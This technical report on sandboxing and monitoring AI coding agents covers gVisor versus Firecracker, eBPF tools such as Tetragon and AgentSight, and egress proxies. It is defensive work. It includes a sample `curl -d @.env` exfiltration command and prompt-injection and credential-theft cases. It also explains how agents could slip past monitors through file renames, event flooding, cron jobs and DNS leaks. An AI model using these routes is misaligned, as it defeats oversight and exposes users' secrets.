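Copies made from one snapshot begin with identical memory. Many programs generate random numbers by repeatedly transforming a secret starting value held in memory, so programs in two copied guests can produce the same sequence. Graf (2021) warned that cloned programs could create duplicate identifiers and temporary encryption keys. Two agents might then overwrite each other's database records, or an attacker who controlled one guest might predict a key used in the other.

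The Linux kernel's own random numbers are safer. Two copies that read `/dev/urandom`, the kernel's usual source, don't get identical results, because the kernel mixes in timer readings and output from the processor's random number generator, according to the Firecracker project. Newer versions of Firecracker also give the guest a virtual device called VMGenID, which holds a random 128-bit number that changes each time a guest resumes from a snapshot. Linux 5.18 and later versions reseed their random number generator when this number changes. AWS's *#SnapSafety* (2024) calls this "slightly racy". The guest has to process a notification first, so a program might ask for a random number before the kernel has reseeded.

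None of this resets a random number generator that a program keeps in its own memory. Firecracker's *Entropy for Clones* warns that the protection covers only the kernel's interfaces and that some programs and libraries remain exposed. AWS therefore tells customers of its Lambda MicroVMs service to use cryptographic libraries that draw on the kernel's random numbers. It also supplies a version of OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, modified to work safely with snapshots. Customers can run their own code after each restore to reset anything else that must be unique.

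If the API key is in memory when the operator takes the snapshot, every virtual machine restored from it will contain the key, so the operator should supply the key only after a restore. Network connections may not survive a restore, so an agent that was downloading a file may have to start again. Firecracker also supports vsock only partly in snapshots.

### Choosing between gVisor and Firecracker

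Agache and colleagues compared Firecracker with other VMMs, while Young and colleagues compared gVisor with ordinary containers. The two groups' timings come from different tests on different machines, so they can't show exactly how much faster one sandbox is than the other, but they do show where each one loses time.

gVisor's main cost is in system calls. In Firecracker, the guest's kernel answers them with no help from the host, and the main costs are booting that kernel and using the disk and network. A build that opens thousands of small files will therefore probably lose less time in Firecracker, especially once the guest's kernel has the files in memory. A job that reads a large amount of new data from disk could lose more.

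gVisor and Firecracker also expose different code to an attacker. Escaping gVisor generally takes a bug in the Sentry and another in the host's kernel, which the Sentry could reach through 55 system calls in 2019 and can reach through some more today. In Firecracker, an attacker gains little by taking over the guest's kernel. Escaping usually still takes a bug in one of Firecracker's few devices and then another in the host's kernel, which the attacker can reach through only 24 system calls and a set of ioctls.

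Those counts make Firecracker look safer than it is, because they leave out KVM. A guest can reach KVM's code by executing certain instructions, and one serious bug there could be enough to give the guest control of the host. gVisor's default platform doesn't use KVM. Ghosh still considers a microVM with a small device model the strongest isolation that starts fast enough to use for every job. This is reasonable because emulating a disk is much simpler than reimplementing Linux, but neither Ghosh nor Agache and colleagues tested such a microVM against gVisor.

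Firecracker is more compatible with existing software than gVisor. Agache and colleagues found no software that failed in a microVM except software that needs particular hardware. The guest runs a real Linux kernel, so it avoids mistakes like gVisor's error in `poll`. However, the operator has to choose a kernel with the features the project needs, and a project that must be tested on Windows needs a different VMM.

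gVisor is the better choice for work on graphics processors, since it can relay a program's requests to the host's drivers. Firecracker's developers removed the graphics code from the VMM they started with, and AWS's *Announcing the Firecracker Open Source Technology* rules out accelerators and direct access to the host's hardware. This rarely matters to an agent that fixes Python tests and calls its model over the network. It does matter to one that trains models.

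gVisor also runs on more machines. Firecracker needs KVM, and therefore either a physical server or a rented virtual machine whose provider allows nested virtualization, which means running one virtual machine inside another. AWS runs Lambda's microVMs on physical servers. Tencent's engineers preferred gVisor because ordinary rented machines are enough for it.

Finally, gVisor and Firecracker differ in what the operator can record. gVisor's trace points can show each file that a program opens and each process it starts. From outside a microVM, the operator can see only disk blocks, packets and whatever the helper program reports. Fuller records have to come from inside the guest, where code that has taken over its kernel can falsify them.

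### MicroVMs in use, in the cloud and on a Mac

Several companies that rent out sandboxes for agents use microVMs. Prasakis names E2B and Vercel Sandbox as users of Firecracker. Northflank runs its sandboxes mainly on Cloud Hypervisor and uses Firecracker or gVisor for some workloads. These companies seem to base their choice of VMM on the job as much as on security.

Firecracker needs KVM, which is part of Linux, so developers who run agents on their own Macs can't use it directly. In Prasakis's survey, 60% of coding-agent users used macOS, and Prasakis built SideKernel for them with Apple's Virtualization framework in place of KVM. Of the 33 respondents who had used a sandbox for agents, eight had trouble with network connections, eight had to set up all their tools again, and seven found it hard or slow to share files. Of the 35 who had never used one, 21 had never considered it. These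 groups are small, but inconvenience and lack of awareness both seem to keep people from using sandboxes.

SideKernel is designed to make the virtual machine feel like the developer's own computer. One command starts a new microVM and shares the current folder with it. SideKernel also forwards network ports and keeps installed packages for the next session if the user saves them. A proxy on the Mac adds the agent's login details to its model requests, so those details normally stay out of the virtual machine.

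Some of these conveniences reduce security. The shared folder is the kind of interface that Firecracker's developers rejected, and an agent can delete anything in it. Automatic port forwarding could connect the Mac to a malicious service in the guest. The network switch either permits all outgoing traffic or blocks everything except the connection to Anthropic's model. In the test-fixing job, the user would have to turn blocking off to reach pypi.org, which would also allow the planted instruction to work.

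Prasakis compared SideKernel with four similar products on 23 tests of features such as file sharing and saved settings. SideKernel and Docker Sandboxes each passed 19, and the other three products passed 12. The scores are weak evidence of which is easiest to use, because each test only checked whether a feature existed, and Prasakis wrote both the tests and SideKernel. Docker Sandboxes did better on networking, passing all five tests to SideKernel's three. It can allow chosen destinations and list the sites the agent contacted, while SideKernel can do neither. SideKernel also hasn't had a formal security review.

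### What a smaller device model leaves exposed

Capable models have broken out of general-purpose virtual machines in tests. *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) concludes that current sandboxes, including Firecracker, are insufficient for agents, and proposes confidential virtual machines, whose memory the processor protects even from the host.

A smaller device model reduces the risk. Each emulated device is code that reads requests from a possibly hostile guest, and a bug in that code can give the guest control of the VMM. Firecracker has no virtual sound card or USB controller, so attackers can't exploit bugs in those devices. Reviewers also have a better chance of finding the remaining bugs when there is less code to read.

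But the guest also depends on code that no VMM can remove. Firecracker passes the guest's disk and network traffic to the host's kernel, and the October 2026 flaw that Cybernews described was in the host's networking code. Leaving out the network card, as Tracekit Box does, should prevent attacks through that code, but it doesn't protect against bugs in KVM. iximiuz Labs had to suspend its course *Running Firecracker Under the Jailer* because it turned off nested virtualization after a series of serious flaws in KVM and the Linux kernel.

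Agache and colleagues cite earlier research showing that only 3% of kernel bugs were in frequently used code, and in their experience a VMM relies mostly on such code. This is a reason for confidence, but a weaker one now that AI systems can search for bugs in code that people have already examined. GhostLock, a bug in the code behind regular threading calls, is also a counterexample.

Side channels also bypass the device model, because two guests that share a processor can affect each other's timing. Agache and colleagues recommend turning off hyper-threading, which lets two programs share a core at once, and turning off the merging of identical memory pages. AWS does both for Lambda, which reduces performance somewhat. It fixes newly found flaws by replacing the whole software image on each host, then checks that every machine has the update. An operator who gives each agent job a new microVM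 can update hosts this way with little disruption, because a host can restart as soon as its current jobs finish.

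## eBPF: recording and blocking actions from inside the kernel

eBPF is a part of Linux that lets an administrator add small programs to a running kernel. The name stands for "extended Berkeley Packet Filter", because the original version selected network packets. Seccomp filters still use that older version. An eBPF program can run at many more points in the kernel, read the kernel's own information about a process or file, and store data between events. Monitoring tools use these programs as probes to record what other software does, and some tools can also block it.

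### From source code to a running probe

Developers usually write a probe in C and compile it into bytecode, instructions for a simple virtual processor. A loader with administrator rights submits the bytecode to the kernel, whose verifier must approve it before it can run. According to *eBPF verifier* in the Linux kernel documentation, the verifier first traces the program's jumps and rejects the program if it contains loops or unreachable instructions, although newer kernels permit loops with a fixed limit. It then simulates every possible path through the program and tracks what each register could contain.

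For example, a probe starts with the address of the event's data in register R1. If the probe adds R1 to itself, the verifier treats the result as a plain number instead of a valid address and rejects any attempt to read memory through it. The verifier also tracks the range of values a number can have. If a probe tests whether a number is greater than 8, the verifier sets its minimum to 9 on one branch and its maximum to 8 on the other. A probe may read bytes 12 and 13 of a packet only after checking that the packet has at least 14 bytes, because bytes are numbered from zero. To save time, the verifier skips the rest of a path when it reaches an instruction it has already approved under conditions at least as broad.

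These checks protect the kernel from the probe, but a badly designed probe can pass them and still miss important events.

After approval, the loader attaches the probe to a hook, the point where it will run. Tracepoints are markers that kernel developers placed at events such as the start of a program, and they change little between versions. A kprobe can attach to almost any kernel function, but a kernel update can change or remove that function. A uprobe attaches to a function in an ordinary program or library. Linux Security Modules (LSM) hooks are placed where the kernel checks whether to allow an operation, and a probe there can refuse it.

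Probes usually report through a ring buffer, a fixed block of memory that the kernel shares with a monitoring program. The probe reserves space for a record, fills it in and submits it for the monitoring program to read later. According to Debian's *ringbuf.rst*, the verifier rejects any probe that could reserve space without then submitting or discarding the record. A reservation fails if the buffer is full. The Linux kernel documentation's *BPF ring buffer* adds that a probe running during certain urgent interrupts can fail to get space even when some is free. In either case the probe can't wait, so the action it was recording, such as opening a file or starting a program, still goes ahead, but the monitoring program gets no record of it.

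### Tetragon: a rule about one file

Tetragon is an open-source tool that uses eBPF for monitoring and enforcement. It belongs to Cilium, a networking and security project for Kubernetes. By default it records when each process starts and ends. According to Tetragon's *Concepts*, a record includes the program, its arguments, its working directory, the time, the container and the parent process. To record anything else, the operator writes a tracing policy that names a hook, the arguments to read and the conditions for a match.

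Suppose the API key in the test-fixing job is stored in a file, `/work/.env`. This policy records every attempt to open it:

```yaml
apiVersion: cilium.io/v1alpha1
kind: TracingPolicy
metadata:
  name: "agent-key-file"
spec:
  lsmhooks:
  - hook: "file_open"
    args:
    - index: 0
      type: "file"
    selectors:
    - matchArgs:
      - index: 0
        operator: "Equal"
        values:
        - "/work/.env"
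```

If the agent obeys the planted line in the README and uses `curl` to send the file to an outside server, Tetragon produces a record like this one, shortened here and with invented values:

```json
{
  "process_lsm": {
    "process": {
      "pid": 5269,
      "cwd": "/work",
      "binary": "/usr/bin/curl",
      "arguments": "-d @.env https://collector.example"
    },
    "parent": { "binary": "/bin/bash" },
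    "function_name": "file_open",
    "policy_name": "agent-key-file",
    "args": [{ "file_arg": { "path": "/work/.env" } }]
  }
}
```

The record links the key file to the program that opened it and, because `curl` takes its destination as an argument, to the server. If the agent had put the key itself on the command line, the log would contain the key. Tetragon can replace secrets with asterisks, but only if the operator has already written a pattern that matches them.

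A key in an environment variable is harder to monitor. A program reads its environment variables from its own memory without a system call, so the first sign of theft is likely to be the outgoing connection.

The same policy can also block the operation. If the operator adds the action `Override` with an error value of -1, `curl` gets an error instead of the file. Tetragon's *Enforcement* explains that the overridden function never runs, and that in general only system calls and security checks can be overridden. The action `Sigkill` ends the process immediately but doesn't always stop the operation that triggered it. For example, a process killed during a `write` may already have written its data. Tetragon's documentation therefore recommends combining the two actions to keep an operation from finishing.

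Neither action stops the agent itself, which may then try another program. The rule also works only if nothing in the job needs the file. If the test suite has to read `.env`, the operator could exempt Python, but the agent could then write a Python script that sends the key.

Enforcement can also have gaps when a container starts or Tetragon stops. Kubernetes may notify Tetragon of a new container only after the container has started running. A separate runtime hook prevents this gap by setting up the policy before the container starts, and the operator can make containers fail to start if Tetragon is unreachable. If Tetragon stops, the `--keep-sensors-on-exit` option leaves the blocking rules in force, but Tetragon records no events until it restarts. Some kernels also lack the build option that `Override` needs on ordinary kernel functions. A policy can then load normally and block nothing,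 so it's worth testing each rule by attempting the action it should block.

### Why the security hook is the better place to check

When a program calls `openat`, it gives the kernel the memory address of a file name. A probe at the entry to the system call can read the name there, find `notes.txt` and let the call through. But another thread in the same program can change the name to `.env` before the kernel makes its own copy. This is a time-of-check to time-of-use attack. More simply, an attacker can make `notes.txt` a symbolic link to `.env`. The attacker can also avoid `openat`, since Linux has other system calls for opening files, and io_uring can open them without a separate system call for each one.

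By the time the kernel reaches the `file_open` hook, it has copied the file name, followed any links and found the file. The probe receives the kernel's own record of that file, which the program can't alter. The usual ways of opening a file all pass through this hook, so one rule covers them.

According to Tetragon's front page, blocking in the kernel avoids time-of-check attacks. This is true of the policy above but not of every Tetragon policy. One example in Tetragon's documentation checks a file name at the entry to `symlinkat`, when the program could still change it.

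An agent could also get around the security hook, because the policy looks for a particular path. The agent could rename `.env` to `notes.txt` and then open it under the new name. The policy would miss the rename because it doesn't open the file, and miss the later open because the path no longer matches. A complete rule would also have to cover renames and hard links, which give one file several names.

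### AgentSight: linking the model's words to system calls

Tetragon can show that `curl` opened the key file, but not that an instruction in a README caused it. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) is designed to recover that link by monitoring an agent at two boundaries: its encrypted connection to the model and its requests to the kernel.

To capture model traffic, AgentSight attaches uprobes to `SSL_write` and `SSL_read`, the functions in OpenSSL and similar libraries that programs call to send and receive encrypted data. The probes copy the text just before encryption or just after decryption, so AgentSight needs no proxy or changes to the agent. Other probes record new processes, opened files and network connections. A filter in the kernel checks each new process's parent and passes on only events from the agent and its descendants.

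A program outside the kernel then links the two streams using three clues. The process must descend from the agent, the action should follow a model response within 100 to 500 milliseconds, and a file name, address or command in the response should reappear in the system call's arguments. A second language model reads the linked events and writes an assessment of anything suspicious.

In the test-fixing job, this should work well if the model's response contains the `curl` command, but less well if the response contains only the command to run the tests and a malicious package steals the key three minutes later. The theft would still come from a descendant of the agent's process, but it would fall outside the time window and match nothing in the response.

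Zheng and colleagues measured AgentSight's overhead with Claude Code on three tasks, running each three times with it and three times without. Summarising a repository took 3.4% longer (132.33 seconds instead of 127.98), writing code took 4.9% longer (23.64 instead of 22.54), and compiling a project took 0.4% longer (92.72 instead of 92.40). In *AgentLoupe*, Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026) repeated the comparison with a newer version of Claude Code and five runs per task, and found overheads of 4.5%, 2.5% and 1.7% for similar tasks. Both sets average 2.9%, but the figures for individual tasks differ so much that they probably reflect variation in the model's response time as well as the time added by the probes. In one of Bao and colleagues' tests, compiling was 0.1% faster with a monitor running. AgentSight clearly adds little overhead for an agent that spends most of its time waiting for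 a model, but these tests can't measure that overhead to within a percentage point.

The first of three case studies resembles the test-fixing job. Zheng and colleagues told an agent to download and build a C project whose README linked to a web page with a hidden instruction. The agent followed the instruction and sent `/etc/passwd`, the system's list of user accounts, to an outside server. AgentSight captured 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model identified the attack. In the second case, an agent kept repeating a web search with the same wrong arguments, and AgentSight traced the loop to the tool error. In the third, six coding agents worked on one project. Even after merging, there were 3,153 events, which showed agents waiting for each other to release locked files.

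These cases show that the linked records can be useful, but not how often AgentSight would catch an attack. The study describes one injection and doesn't report how many harmless sessions the second model would flag. That model also reads the attacker's text as part of the trace, so an attacker could try to mislead it too.

Hostile code can encrypt data with its own library, where AgentSight has no probe. The kernel would still handle the connection, but AgentSight couldn't read what the code sent. Zheng and colleagues describe both boundaries as tamper-proof, which is too strong for the encryption library.

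### What later versions of AgentSight added

eunomia-bpf's *AgentSight* describes version 1.0.29, which is closer to a finished product. It saves each recorded session in a database and can list the processes, file accesses and model calls afterwards. It can also export model calls in the format of OpenTelemetry, a common standard for monitoring data. Claude Code and programs built on Node.js include their encryption library in their own program file, so probes on the system's library miss their traffic. Newer versions of AgentSight find the right functions in these files.

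AgentSight still can't trace the code editor Cursor through eBPF, partly because Cursor usually runs on macOS or Windows and uses a different message format. Instead, AgentSight reads the session files that Cursor saves. These files are convenient for tracking costs but are weaker evidence in an investigation, because the software under investigation wrote them.

By default, AgentSight saves its database in the current directory, which will often be the project folder, where the agent could delete it. The database may also contain prompts, file paths and the headers of network requests, so it needs as much protection as the agent's credentials.

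### Actions that continue after the agent stops

An agent can write a script, schedule it to run an hour later, and then exit. Because cron, the system's scheduler, starts the script, the new process doesn't descend from the agent. An hour is also far longer than AgentSight's time window. Bao and colleagues therefore argue that AgentSight would fail to link the script to the agent. They base this on AgentSight's design and haven't yet run the two tools on the same attack, but the argument is convincing.

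The researchers' own tool, AgentLoupe, numbers each new prompt and labels whatever follows from it with that number. Child processes inherit the label. When a labelled process writes a file, the file gets the label, and any process that later opens the file picks it up. In a test with the job scheduler cron, AgentLoupe traced a reverse shell, a connection that gives an attacker a command line, back to the request that created it. In a second test, one session planted an instruction in AGENTS.md, a file of standing instructions for coding agents, and AgentLoupe linked it to a command that a later session ran. The tool increased the running time of the three benchmark tasks by 4.5% to 8.0%.

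Labels can also spread to programs unrelated to the agent's work. For example, a backup program that reads the project folder would pick up the agent's label. AgentLoupe has rules to limit this, but Bao and colleagues haven't measured how many false links it creates or real ones it misses.

*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) uses similar labels for processes and files but doesn't read the model's traffic. Its label stays with a file when an agent renames it, so the renaming trick that gets around Tetragon's path rule would fail. In a stress test that repeatedly created processes and changed files, the system increased running time by 0.2% to 3.5%. It correctly reconstructed one scripted chain of events in all 30 runs of each configuration. It misses io_uring operations and access to memory-mapped files, which programs read and write like ordinary memory. Its file labels also disappear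 when the computer restarts or the kernel removes a file's details from memory to free space.

### What the host can see of each sandbox

A probe on the host can record only what reaches the host's kernel. In an ordinary container, that includes every system call the agent's programs make. gVisor and Firecracker handle most of those calls outside the host's kernel, so the host's records are much less informative.

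| The agent's action | Ordinary container | gVisor | Firecracker |
|---|---|---|---|
| Starts a program | The program, its arguments and its parent | No record of the program or its arguments | No record |
| Opens a project file | The path and the process | Usually an `openat` call by the Sentry | At most, a read from the disk image |
| Connects to a server | The process and the address | Packets from the sandbox | Packets, if the microVM has a network card |

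Some settings change this. For instance, with gVisor's host networking, a probe can record the Sentry's connections. In any of the sandboxes, an eBPF program on the host's network interface can read the addresses on packets, but with gVisor or Firecracker it can't identify which program in the sandbox sent each packet.

AgentSight's uprobes don't work from the host on programs in a microVM, because the host's kernel doesn't manage the guest's processes. If the harness runs on the host and only its commands run in the microVM, AgentSight can still read the model's proposals but can't see the system calls that would show what the commands did.

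The host probe is still useful for detecting escapes. gVisor's normal filter prevents the Sentry from starting other programs, and Firecracker doesn't need to open a shell. If the Sentry starts a program or Firecracker opens a shell on the host, something has almost certainly gone wrong. The sandbox process does the same few things whatever the agent does inside it, so a strict rule is unlikely to raise false alarms.

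To see the agent's actions in detail, the operator has to record them inside the sandbox. gVisor's trace points do this from the Sentry. In Firecracker, Tetragon or AgentSight can run inside the guest if the guest kernel has the eBPF features they need. They can record the same events there as in a container, but they share a kernel with the agent. An agent with administrator rights in the guest can stop the monitor or remove its probes, though with only ordinary rights it would first need a kernel exploit.

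An operator who runs a monitor in the guest should therefore give the agent an ordinary account and send each record to the host immediately, so that anyone who later takes over the guest can't change the records already sent. If the guest suddenly stops sending records, that would also be a reason to stop the job.

### How many events, and how many get lost

An operator can hook almost anything, but the volume of records grows quickly. The following illustrative estimate assumes 1,000 test-fixing jobs a day. Each job starts 200 processes and makes 50 connections, each process opens 100 files, and each open file leads to 20 reads or writes. The estimate also assumes 2 kilobytes per record, roughly the size of the sample process record in Tetragon's documentation.

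| What the operator records | Events per job | Data per job | Data per day |
|---|---|---|---|
| Process starts, process exits and connections | 450 | 0.9 MB | 0.9 GB |
| The above and every file opened | 20,450 | 41 MB | 41 GB |
| The above and every read and write | 420,450 | 841 MB | 841 GB |

The events in the first row are easy to store and would show which programs `pip install` started and where they connected. Those in the third take up about 900 times as much space, and most would describe Python loading its own files. A sensible compromise would be to record all processes and connections but only those file accesses that involve secrets or important settings. Tetragon can apply this filter in the kernel, before a record takes up space in the buffer, but an investigator can't recover an event that the filter discarded.

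Large volumes of events also cause losses. Suppose 100 jobs on one server each make 1,000 reads and writes a second, and each record takes 500 bytes in the buffer. A 64 MiB ring buffer, the size AgentLoupe uses for model traffic, would hold about 134,000 records. If the monitoring program stalled, the buffer would fill in about 1.3 seconds, and new records would then be lost.

Tetragon can limit the number of events it records from each container, but an agent could exploit this by starting thousands of trivial processes, waiting for Tetragon to stop recording that container and then running the program it wants to hide. Tetragon records when this throttling starts and stops, so an investigator would at least know about the gap. A separate option drops repeated events, but it compares only the first 40 bytes of each argument, so it could treat two different files as the same one if their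 long paths begin the same way. AgentLoupe marks a record when part of the model's traffic is missing.

Blocking is less vulnerable to these losses than recording. Tetragon applies its rules in the kernel when the call happens, so a rule against opening the key file still works when the buffer is full.

### Bugs in the verifier and the kernel

Security tools built on eBPF depend on the verifier, which is complicated and has had bugs. In 2020, researchers disclosed an error in how it tracked 32-bit numbers (CVE-2020-8835). A user could load an eBPF program that the verifier wrongly accepted and use it to read and write the kernel's memory.

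An attacker generally has to load an eBPF program to exploit such a bug, which reduces the danger from an agent. Most Linux distributions now let only administrators load one, and Docker's default filter blocks the system call from ordinary containers. The operator can load the probes and still deny eBPF to the agent. However, Tetragon and AgentSight need extensive rights over the host, so a flaw in either could also be serious.

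Cui and colleagues assume that the kernel, the verifier and the program that loads the probes can all be trusted. For an agent in an ordinary container, a flaw such as Copy Fail could break that assumption, because code that takes over the host's kernel can turn off the probes or feed them false information. This is another reason to send records to a different machine quickly, and to combine host probes with a sandbox that makes the host's kernel harder to reach.

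### Agents have no normal pattern of behaviour

Security teams often write rules for a web server by watching what it normally does and blocking everything else. Vaughan, in *eBPF Runtime Observability for Codex CLI*, points out that coding agents are less predictable. The files they open, the programs they run and the network connections they make change with every request. A rule that blocked unfamiliar addresses could block an agent's first attempt to install a package from a new source.

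Vaughan suggests recording widely but blocking only actions that no coding job should need, such as loading a kernel module or reading the system's password file. This is a reasonable starting point because it avoids most false alarms, but it wouldn't protect the API key, since coding agents normally open project files and make web connections. Restricting those connections requires a list of allowed destinations, and a kernel probe usually has only a numerical address to check against it. Many websites can share one address, and a website's address can change.

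Vaughan also argues that kernel records can assure a compliance officer that an agent sent no data to unapproved destinations. These records are better evidence than the agent's own account, but they can't prove the claim on their own, because the monitor may have lost events or the agent may have sent the data through an approved service. The `ping` attack on Claude Code sent the keys out in DNS queries. Such queries may go directly only to the company's own DNS server, which passes them on to the attacker's, so a log of direct connections would show nothing unusual.

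## Network proxies: deciding what may leave the sandbox

Unlike a kernel probe, an egress proxy usually receives the name of the server a program wants to reach. To reach pypi.org over HTTPS, for example, pip sends the proxy the line `CONNECT pypi.org:443`. The proxy looks up the address, opens the connection and copies bytes in both directions. An operator can therefore give the proxy an allowlist of server names and have it refuse all others.

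Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a February 2026 test in which a company researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine work. One step was to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside server, and Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. The instruction came from the user, so defences in the model had nothing suspicious to catch. Anthropic concludes that only limits on file access and outgoing connections would have stopped the attack.

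### Removing every other route

Operators usually direct programs to a proxy with environment variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`. Curl and npm follow these variables, but other programs can ignore them, and a short Python script can open a direct connection. *Proxy domains*, a documentation page from the sandbox provider Blaxel, states that its domain filter depends by default on tools respecting the variables. A customer has to add a firewall rule to enforce the filter.

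One way to make a proxy binding is to write firewall rules for the agent's user account. In *Steerability via constraints* (2026), the rules let that account reach one address and port, where the proxy listens, and reject everything else. On macOS, *Aegis OS* (2026) does much the same with two lines of sandbox policy:

```
(deny network-outbound)
(allow network-outbound (remote ip "localhost:51691"))
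```

On Linux, *Aegis OS* puts the agent in a network namespace with no outside connection. This also cuts the agent off from the proxy, so a small program inside the sandbox listens on the proxy's usual port and forwards traffic to the host through a Unix socket. Other agents' sockets are visible from the sandbox, so each connection must present a random token to prevent one agent from using another's permissions.

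These arrangements need testing, because a forgotten route causes no visible error. *Permission Denied* (2026), a study of coding agents in restricted environments, runs its tests before each agent starts. Some check whether nested shells, numerical addresses, unusual ports or child processes can get around the proxy, and others check that permitted operations still work. If a required test fails, the study discards the sandbox and starts another.

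### Anthropic's sandbox-runtime on a developer's machine

Claude Code's sandbox for shell commands uses Anthropic's open-source package sandbox-runtime. On Linux it runs each command in a disconnected network namespace, and on macOS it uses Seatbelt to block every connection except the one to its proxy. The proxy runs outside the sandbox and checks each requested domain against the user's allow and deny lists.

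According to Anthropic, tools that ignore the proxy variables, including plain `ssh` and most database drivers, can't connect even to an allowed host. Programs that use UDP, the protocol that carries most DNS queries, can't send traffic out. Neither can `ping`, so the `ping` attack described earlier would fail here.

The list of allowed domains starts empty. When a command needs a new host, it waits while Claude Code asks the user, who can allow the host for the session or permanently. In auto mode, Claude instead attaches a list of hosts to the command, and a second model reviews the list and the command together. An approved list applies only while that command runs.

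Anthropic reports that the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%. This also improves security, because users had approved about 93% of prompts and paid less attention as the number grew. Users can still approve the remaining prompts carelessly, so an operator who doesn't want to rely on their approval can set `strictAllowlist`, which makes the proxy refuse unlisted hosts without asking.

Other defaults favour convenience too. The sandbox is off until the user turns it on. If a required program is missing, Claude Code runs commands without the sandbox unless the user has set `failIfUnavailable`. After a command fails, Claude may propose running it again outside the sandbox, and the retry needs no new approval if an existing rule allows the command. Claude's own tools for reading files and fetching web pages always run outside the sandbox, so the domain list doesn't limit them.

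GitLab's *CVE-2025-66479* (2025) describes a serious bug in which sandbox-runtime didn't properly enforce its network sandbox if the policy contained no allowed domains. A policy meant to block all traffic could therefore have let all of it through. Version 0.0.16 fixed this. GitLab runs its own coding agents in sandbox-runtime, and its *Remote execution environment sandbox* now requires version 0.0.20 or later.

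### One connection through Tracekit Box

Tracekit Box runs each job in a Firecracker microVM without a network card and puts more checks between the request and the connection. Its proxy runs on the host, and the guest can reach it only through vsock. The proxy also checks each connection with a signer, a separate program that applies its own rules and signs a record of each decision. The signer comes from Tracekit, an earlier project by Ghosh.

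When pip tries to connect to pypi.org, the proxy first checks whether the name is on the allowlist, which limits the servers the agent can reach. An operator can allow a single name, a name with one port, or all the subdomains of a domain. Ready-made lists cover common needs, and the one for Python contains pypi.org and files.pythonhosted.org, which hosts the package files.

Since pypi.org is on the list, the proxy looks up its address and checks that the address is public. This check is necessary because the owner of a domain can point its name at any address, including an internal one. The proxy refuses addresses that belong to private networks or to the host itself, and those that cloud providers use to give information to their virtual machines, such as 169.254.169.254. On many cloud servers, any program that can reach that address can request the server's credentials.

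Products differ on whether agents can reach private addresses. Docker blocks them by default in its agent sandboxes, while Claude Code's proxy allows a connection to an address such as 10.0.0.5 if it is made through an allowed company hostname. Tracekit Box blocks private addresses whatever the allowlist contains, so its agents can't use a company's internal package server at a private address.

Next, the proxy requests a signed decision from the signer. This step lets an operator forbid a connection that the allowlist would permit, and no connection opens without a signed decision. If the signer doesn't respond, the proxy refuses the connection.

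The proxy then connects to the same address it checked, without a second lookup. This defeats DNS rebinding, in which an attacker's DNS server returns a harmless address for the check and an internal address for the connection.

Before letting any of pip's data through, the proxy makes a final check of the server's name. An HTTPS connection begins with a TLS handshake, in which the two sides agree on encryption keys. Its first message normally contains the server's name in readable form. Many sites can share one server, so a program could ask the proxy for pypi.org and then name a different site in the handshake. The proxy therefore rejects the connection unless the two names match, and it also rejects handshakes that encrypt the name.

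This match blocks only one version of domain fronting, a technique for reaching a forbidden site through an allowed one, though Ghosh presents it as closing off the technique. In the usual version, both visible names are the allowed site's, and the forbidden name appears only in the encrypted request. Some large hosting networks deliver such a request to the forbidden site. The proxy can't detect this unless it decrypts the connection, which by default it does only for certain hosts.

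For a host that isn't on the list, the proxy must get approval before it looks up and checks the address. It sends a request to the signer, then holds the connection for up to two minutes while a person on the host machine decides. This order keeps the agent from leaking data in the host name itself, as the `ping` attack did. The proxy also limits new approval requests to 30 a minute so that an agent can't overwhelm the reviewer.

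In Ghosh's demonstration, the signer's standard rules allowed a connection to example.com, which wasn't on the list. The connection failed only because nobody approved it before `curl` timed out after five seconds, so blocking unlisted hosts depended on human approval. A request for 169.254.169.254 failed immediately. An operator made both requests by hand, and no study has yet tested the system against a capable agent trying to escape.

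### TLS interception

On an ordinary HTTPS connection, a proxy can see the server's name, the port, the timing and the amount of data, but not the page requested, the login details or the content. If the allowlist contains github.com, the proxy can't distinguish an agent that downloads a public library from one that uploads the project to an attacker's account.

TLS interception removes this blind spot. When pip connects to pypi.org, the proxy answers instead, with its own certificate for that name. Programs accept a certificate only if an authority they trust has signed it, so the operator creates a private certificate authority and adds it to the sandbox's trusted list. The proxy opens a second encrypted connection to the real server. It decrypts the traffic from each side, checks it and encrypts it again for the other.

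Anyone who steals the private certificate authority's key can impersonate websites to every program that trusts that authority. Cloudflare (2026) limits this risk by creating a new authority for each sandbox and keeping its key outside the sandbox. Tracekit Box does the same, and also restricts each authority to the hosts whose traffic the proxy needs to read.

Once the proxy can read requests, the operator can write narrower rules. *Avalon-M1* (2026), a study of reinforcement learning, describes a proxy whose rules cover the host, path and HTTP method, so they can distinguish downloads from uploads. When the proxy refuses a request, it immediately returns an error that gives the reason, so tools don't hang. In audit mode, it lets requests through and logs the ones it would have refused, which helps the operator find out what a job needs before enforcing the rules. A job can also have one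 policy for installing its software and a stricter one for the agent, which takes effect before the agent's first command.

### Keys that never enter the sandbox

Interception also lets an agent use a key without holding it. In Tracekit Box, the operator ties each secret to exact host names and to one header, a labelled line at the start of a web request. The agent receives a placeholder instead of the key. For a secret named GH, the placeholder is `tkbox_GH_` followed by 32 random characters. When a request to the right host carries the placeholder in the right header, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real key.

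The proxy blocks the placeholder anywhere else in traffic it can read. It also searches responses for the real key and masks it, because some servers repeat the headers they receive, which would expose the key to the agent. The search covers several common encodings of the key, including base64 and hexadecimal.

In Ghosh's comparison, no other agent sandbox keeps keys out while still letting the agent use them. Anthropic now documents a similar feature for Claude Code, called masking. It requires an experimental setting that turns on interception. Without it, the key's placeholder reaches the server unchanged and the login fails, but the key stays safe. It is also safer to set `injectHosts`, the list of hosts that may receive the key, because otherwise the proxy inserts the key in requests to every allowed domain.

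Simple replacement doesn't work for every service. A program that uses Amazon's cloud signs each request with its secret key instead of sending the key. Claude Code's proxy has to recognise such a request and sign it again with the real key. It can't do this for some kinds of request, including streaming uploads.

An operator can avoid interception if the program lets them change the server address it uses. *Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes nine agents at a healthcare technology company, where an earlier audit had found 12 keys in one agent's shell settings. In the new design, a helper container next to each agent holds the keys. The agent sends its model requests to the helper at a local address, and the helper adds the key and makes its own encrypted connection to the model's provider. This requires no forged certificate, but the helper must support each service separately.

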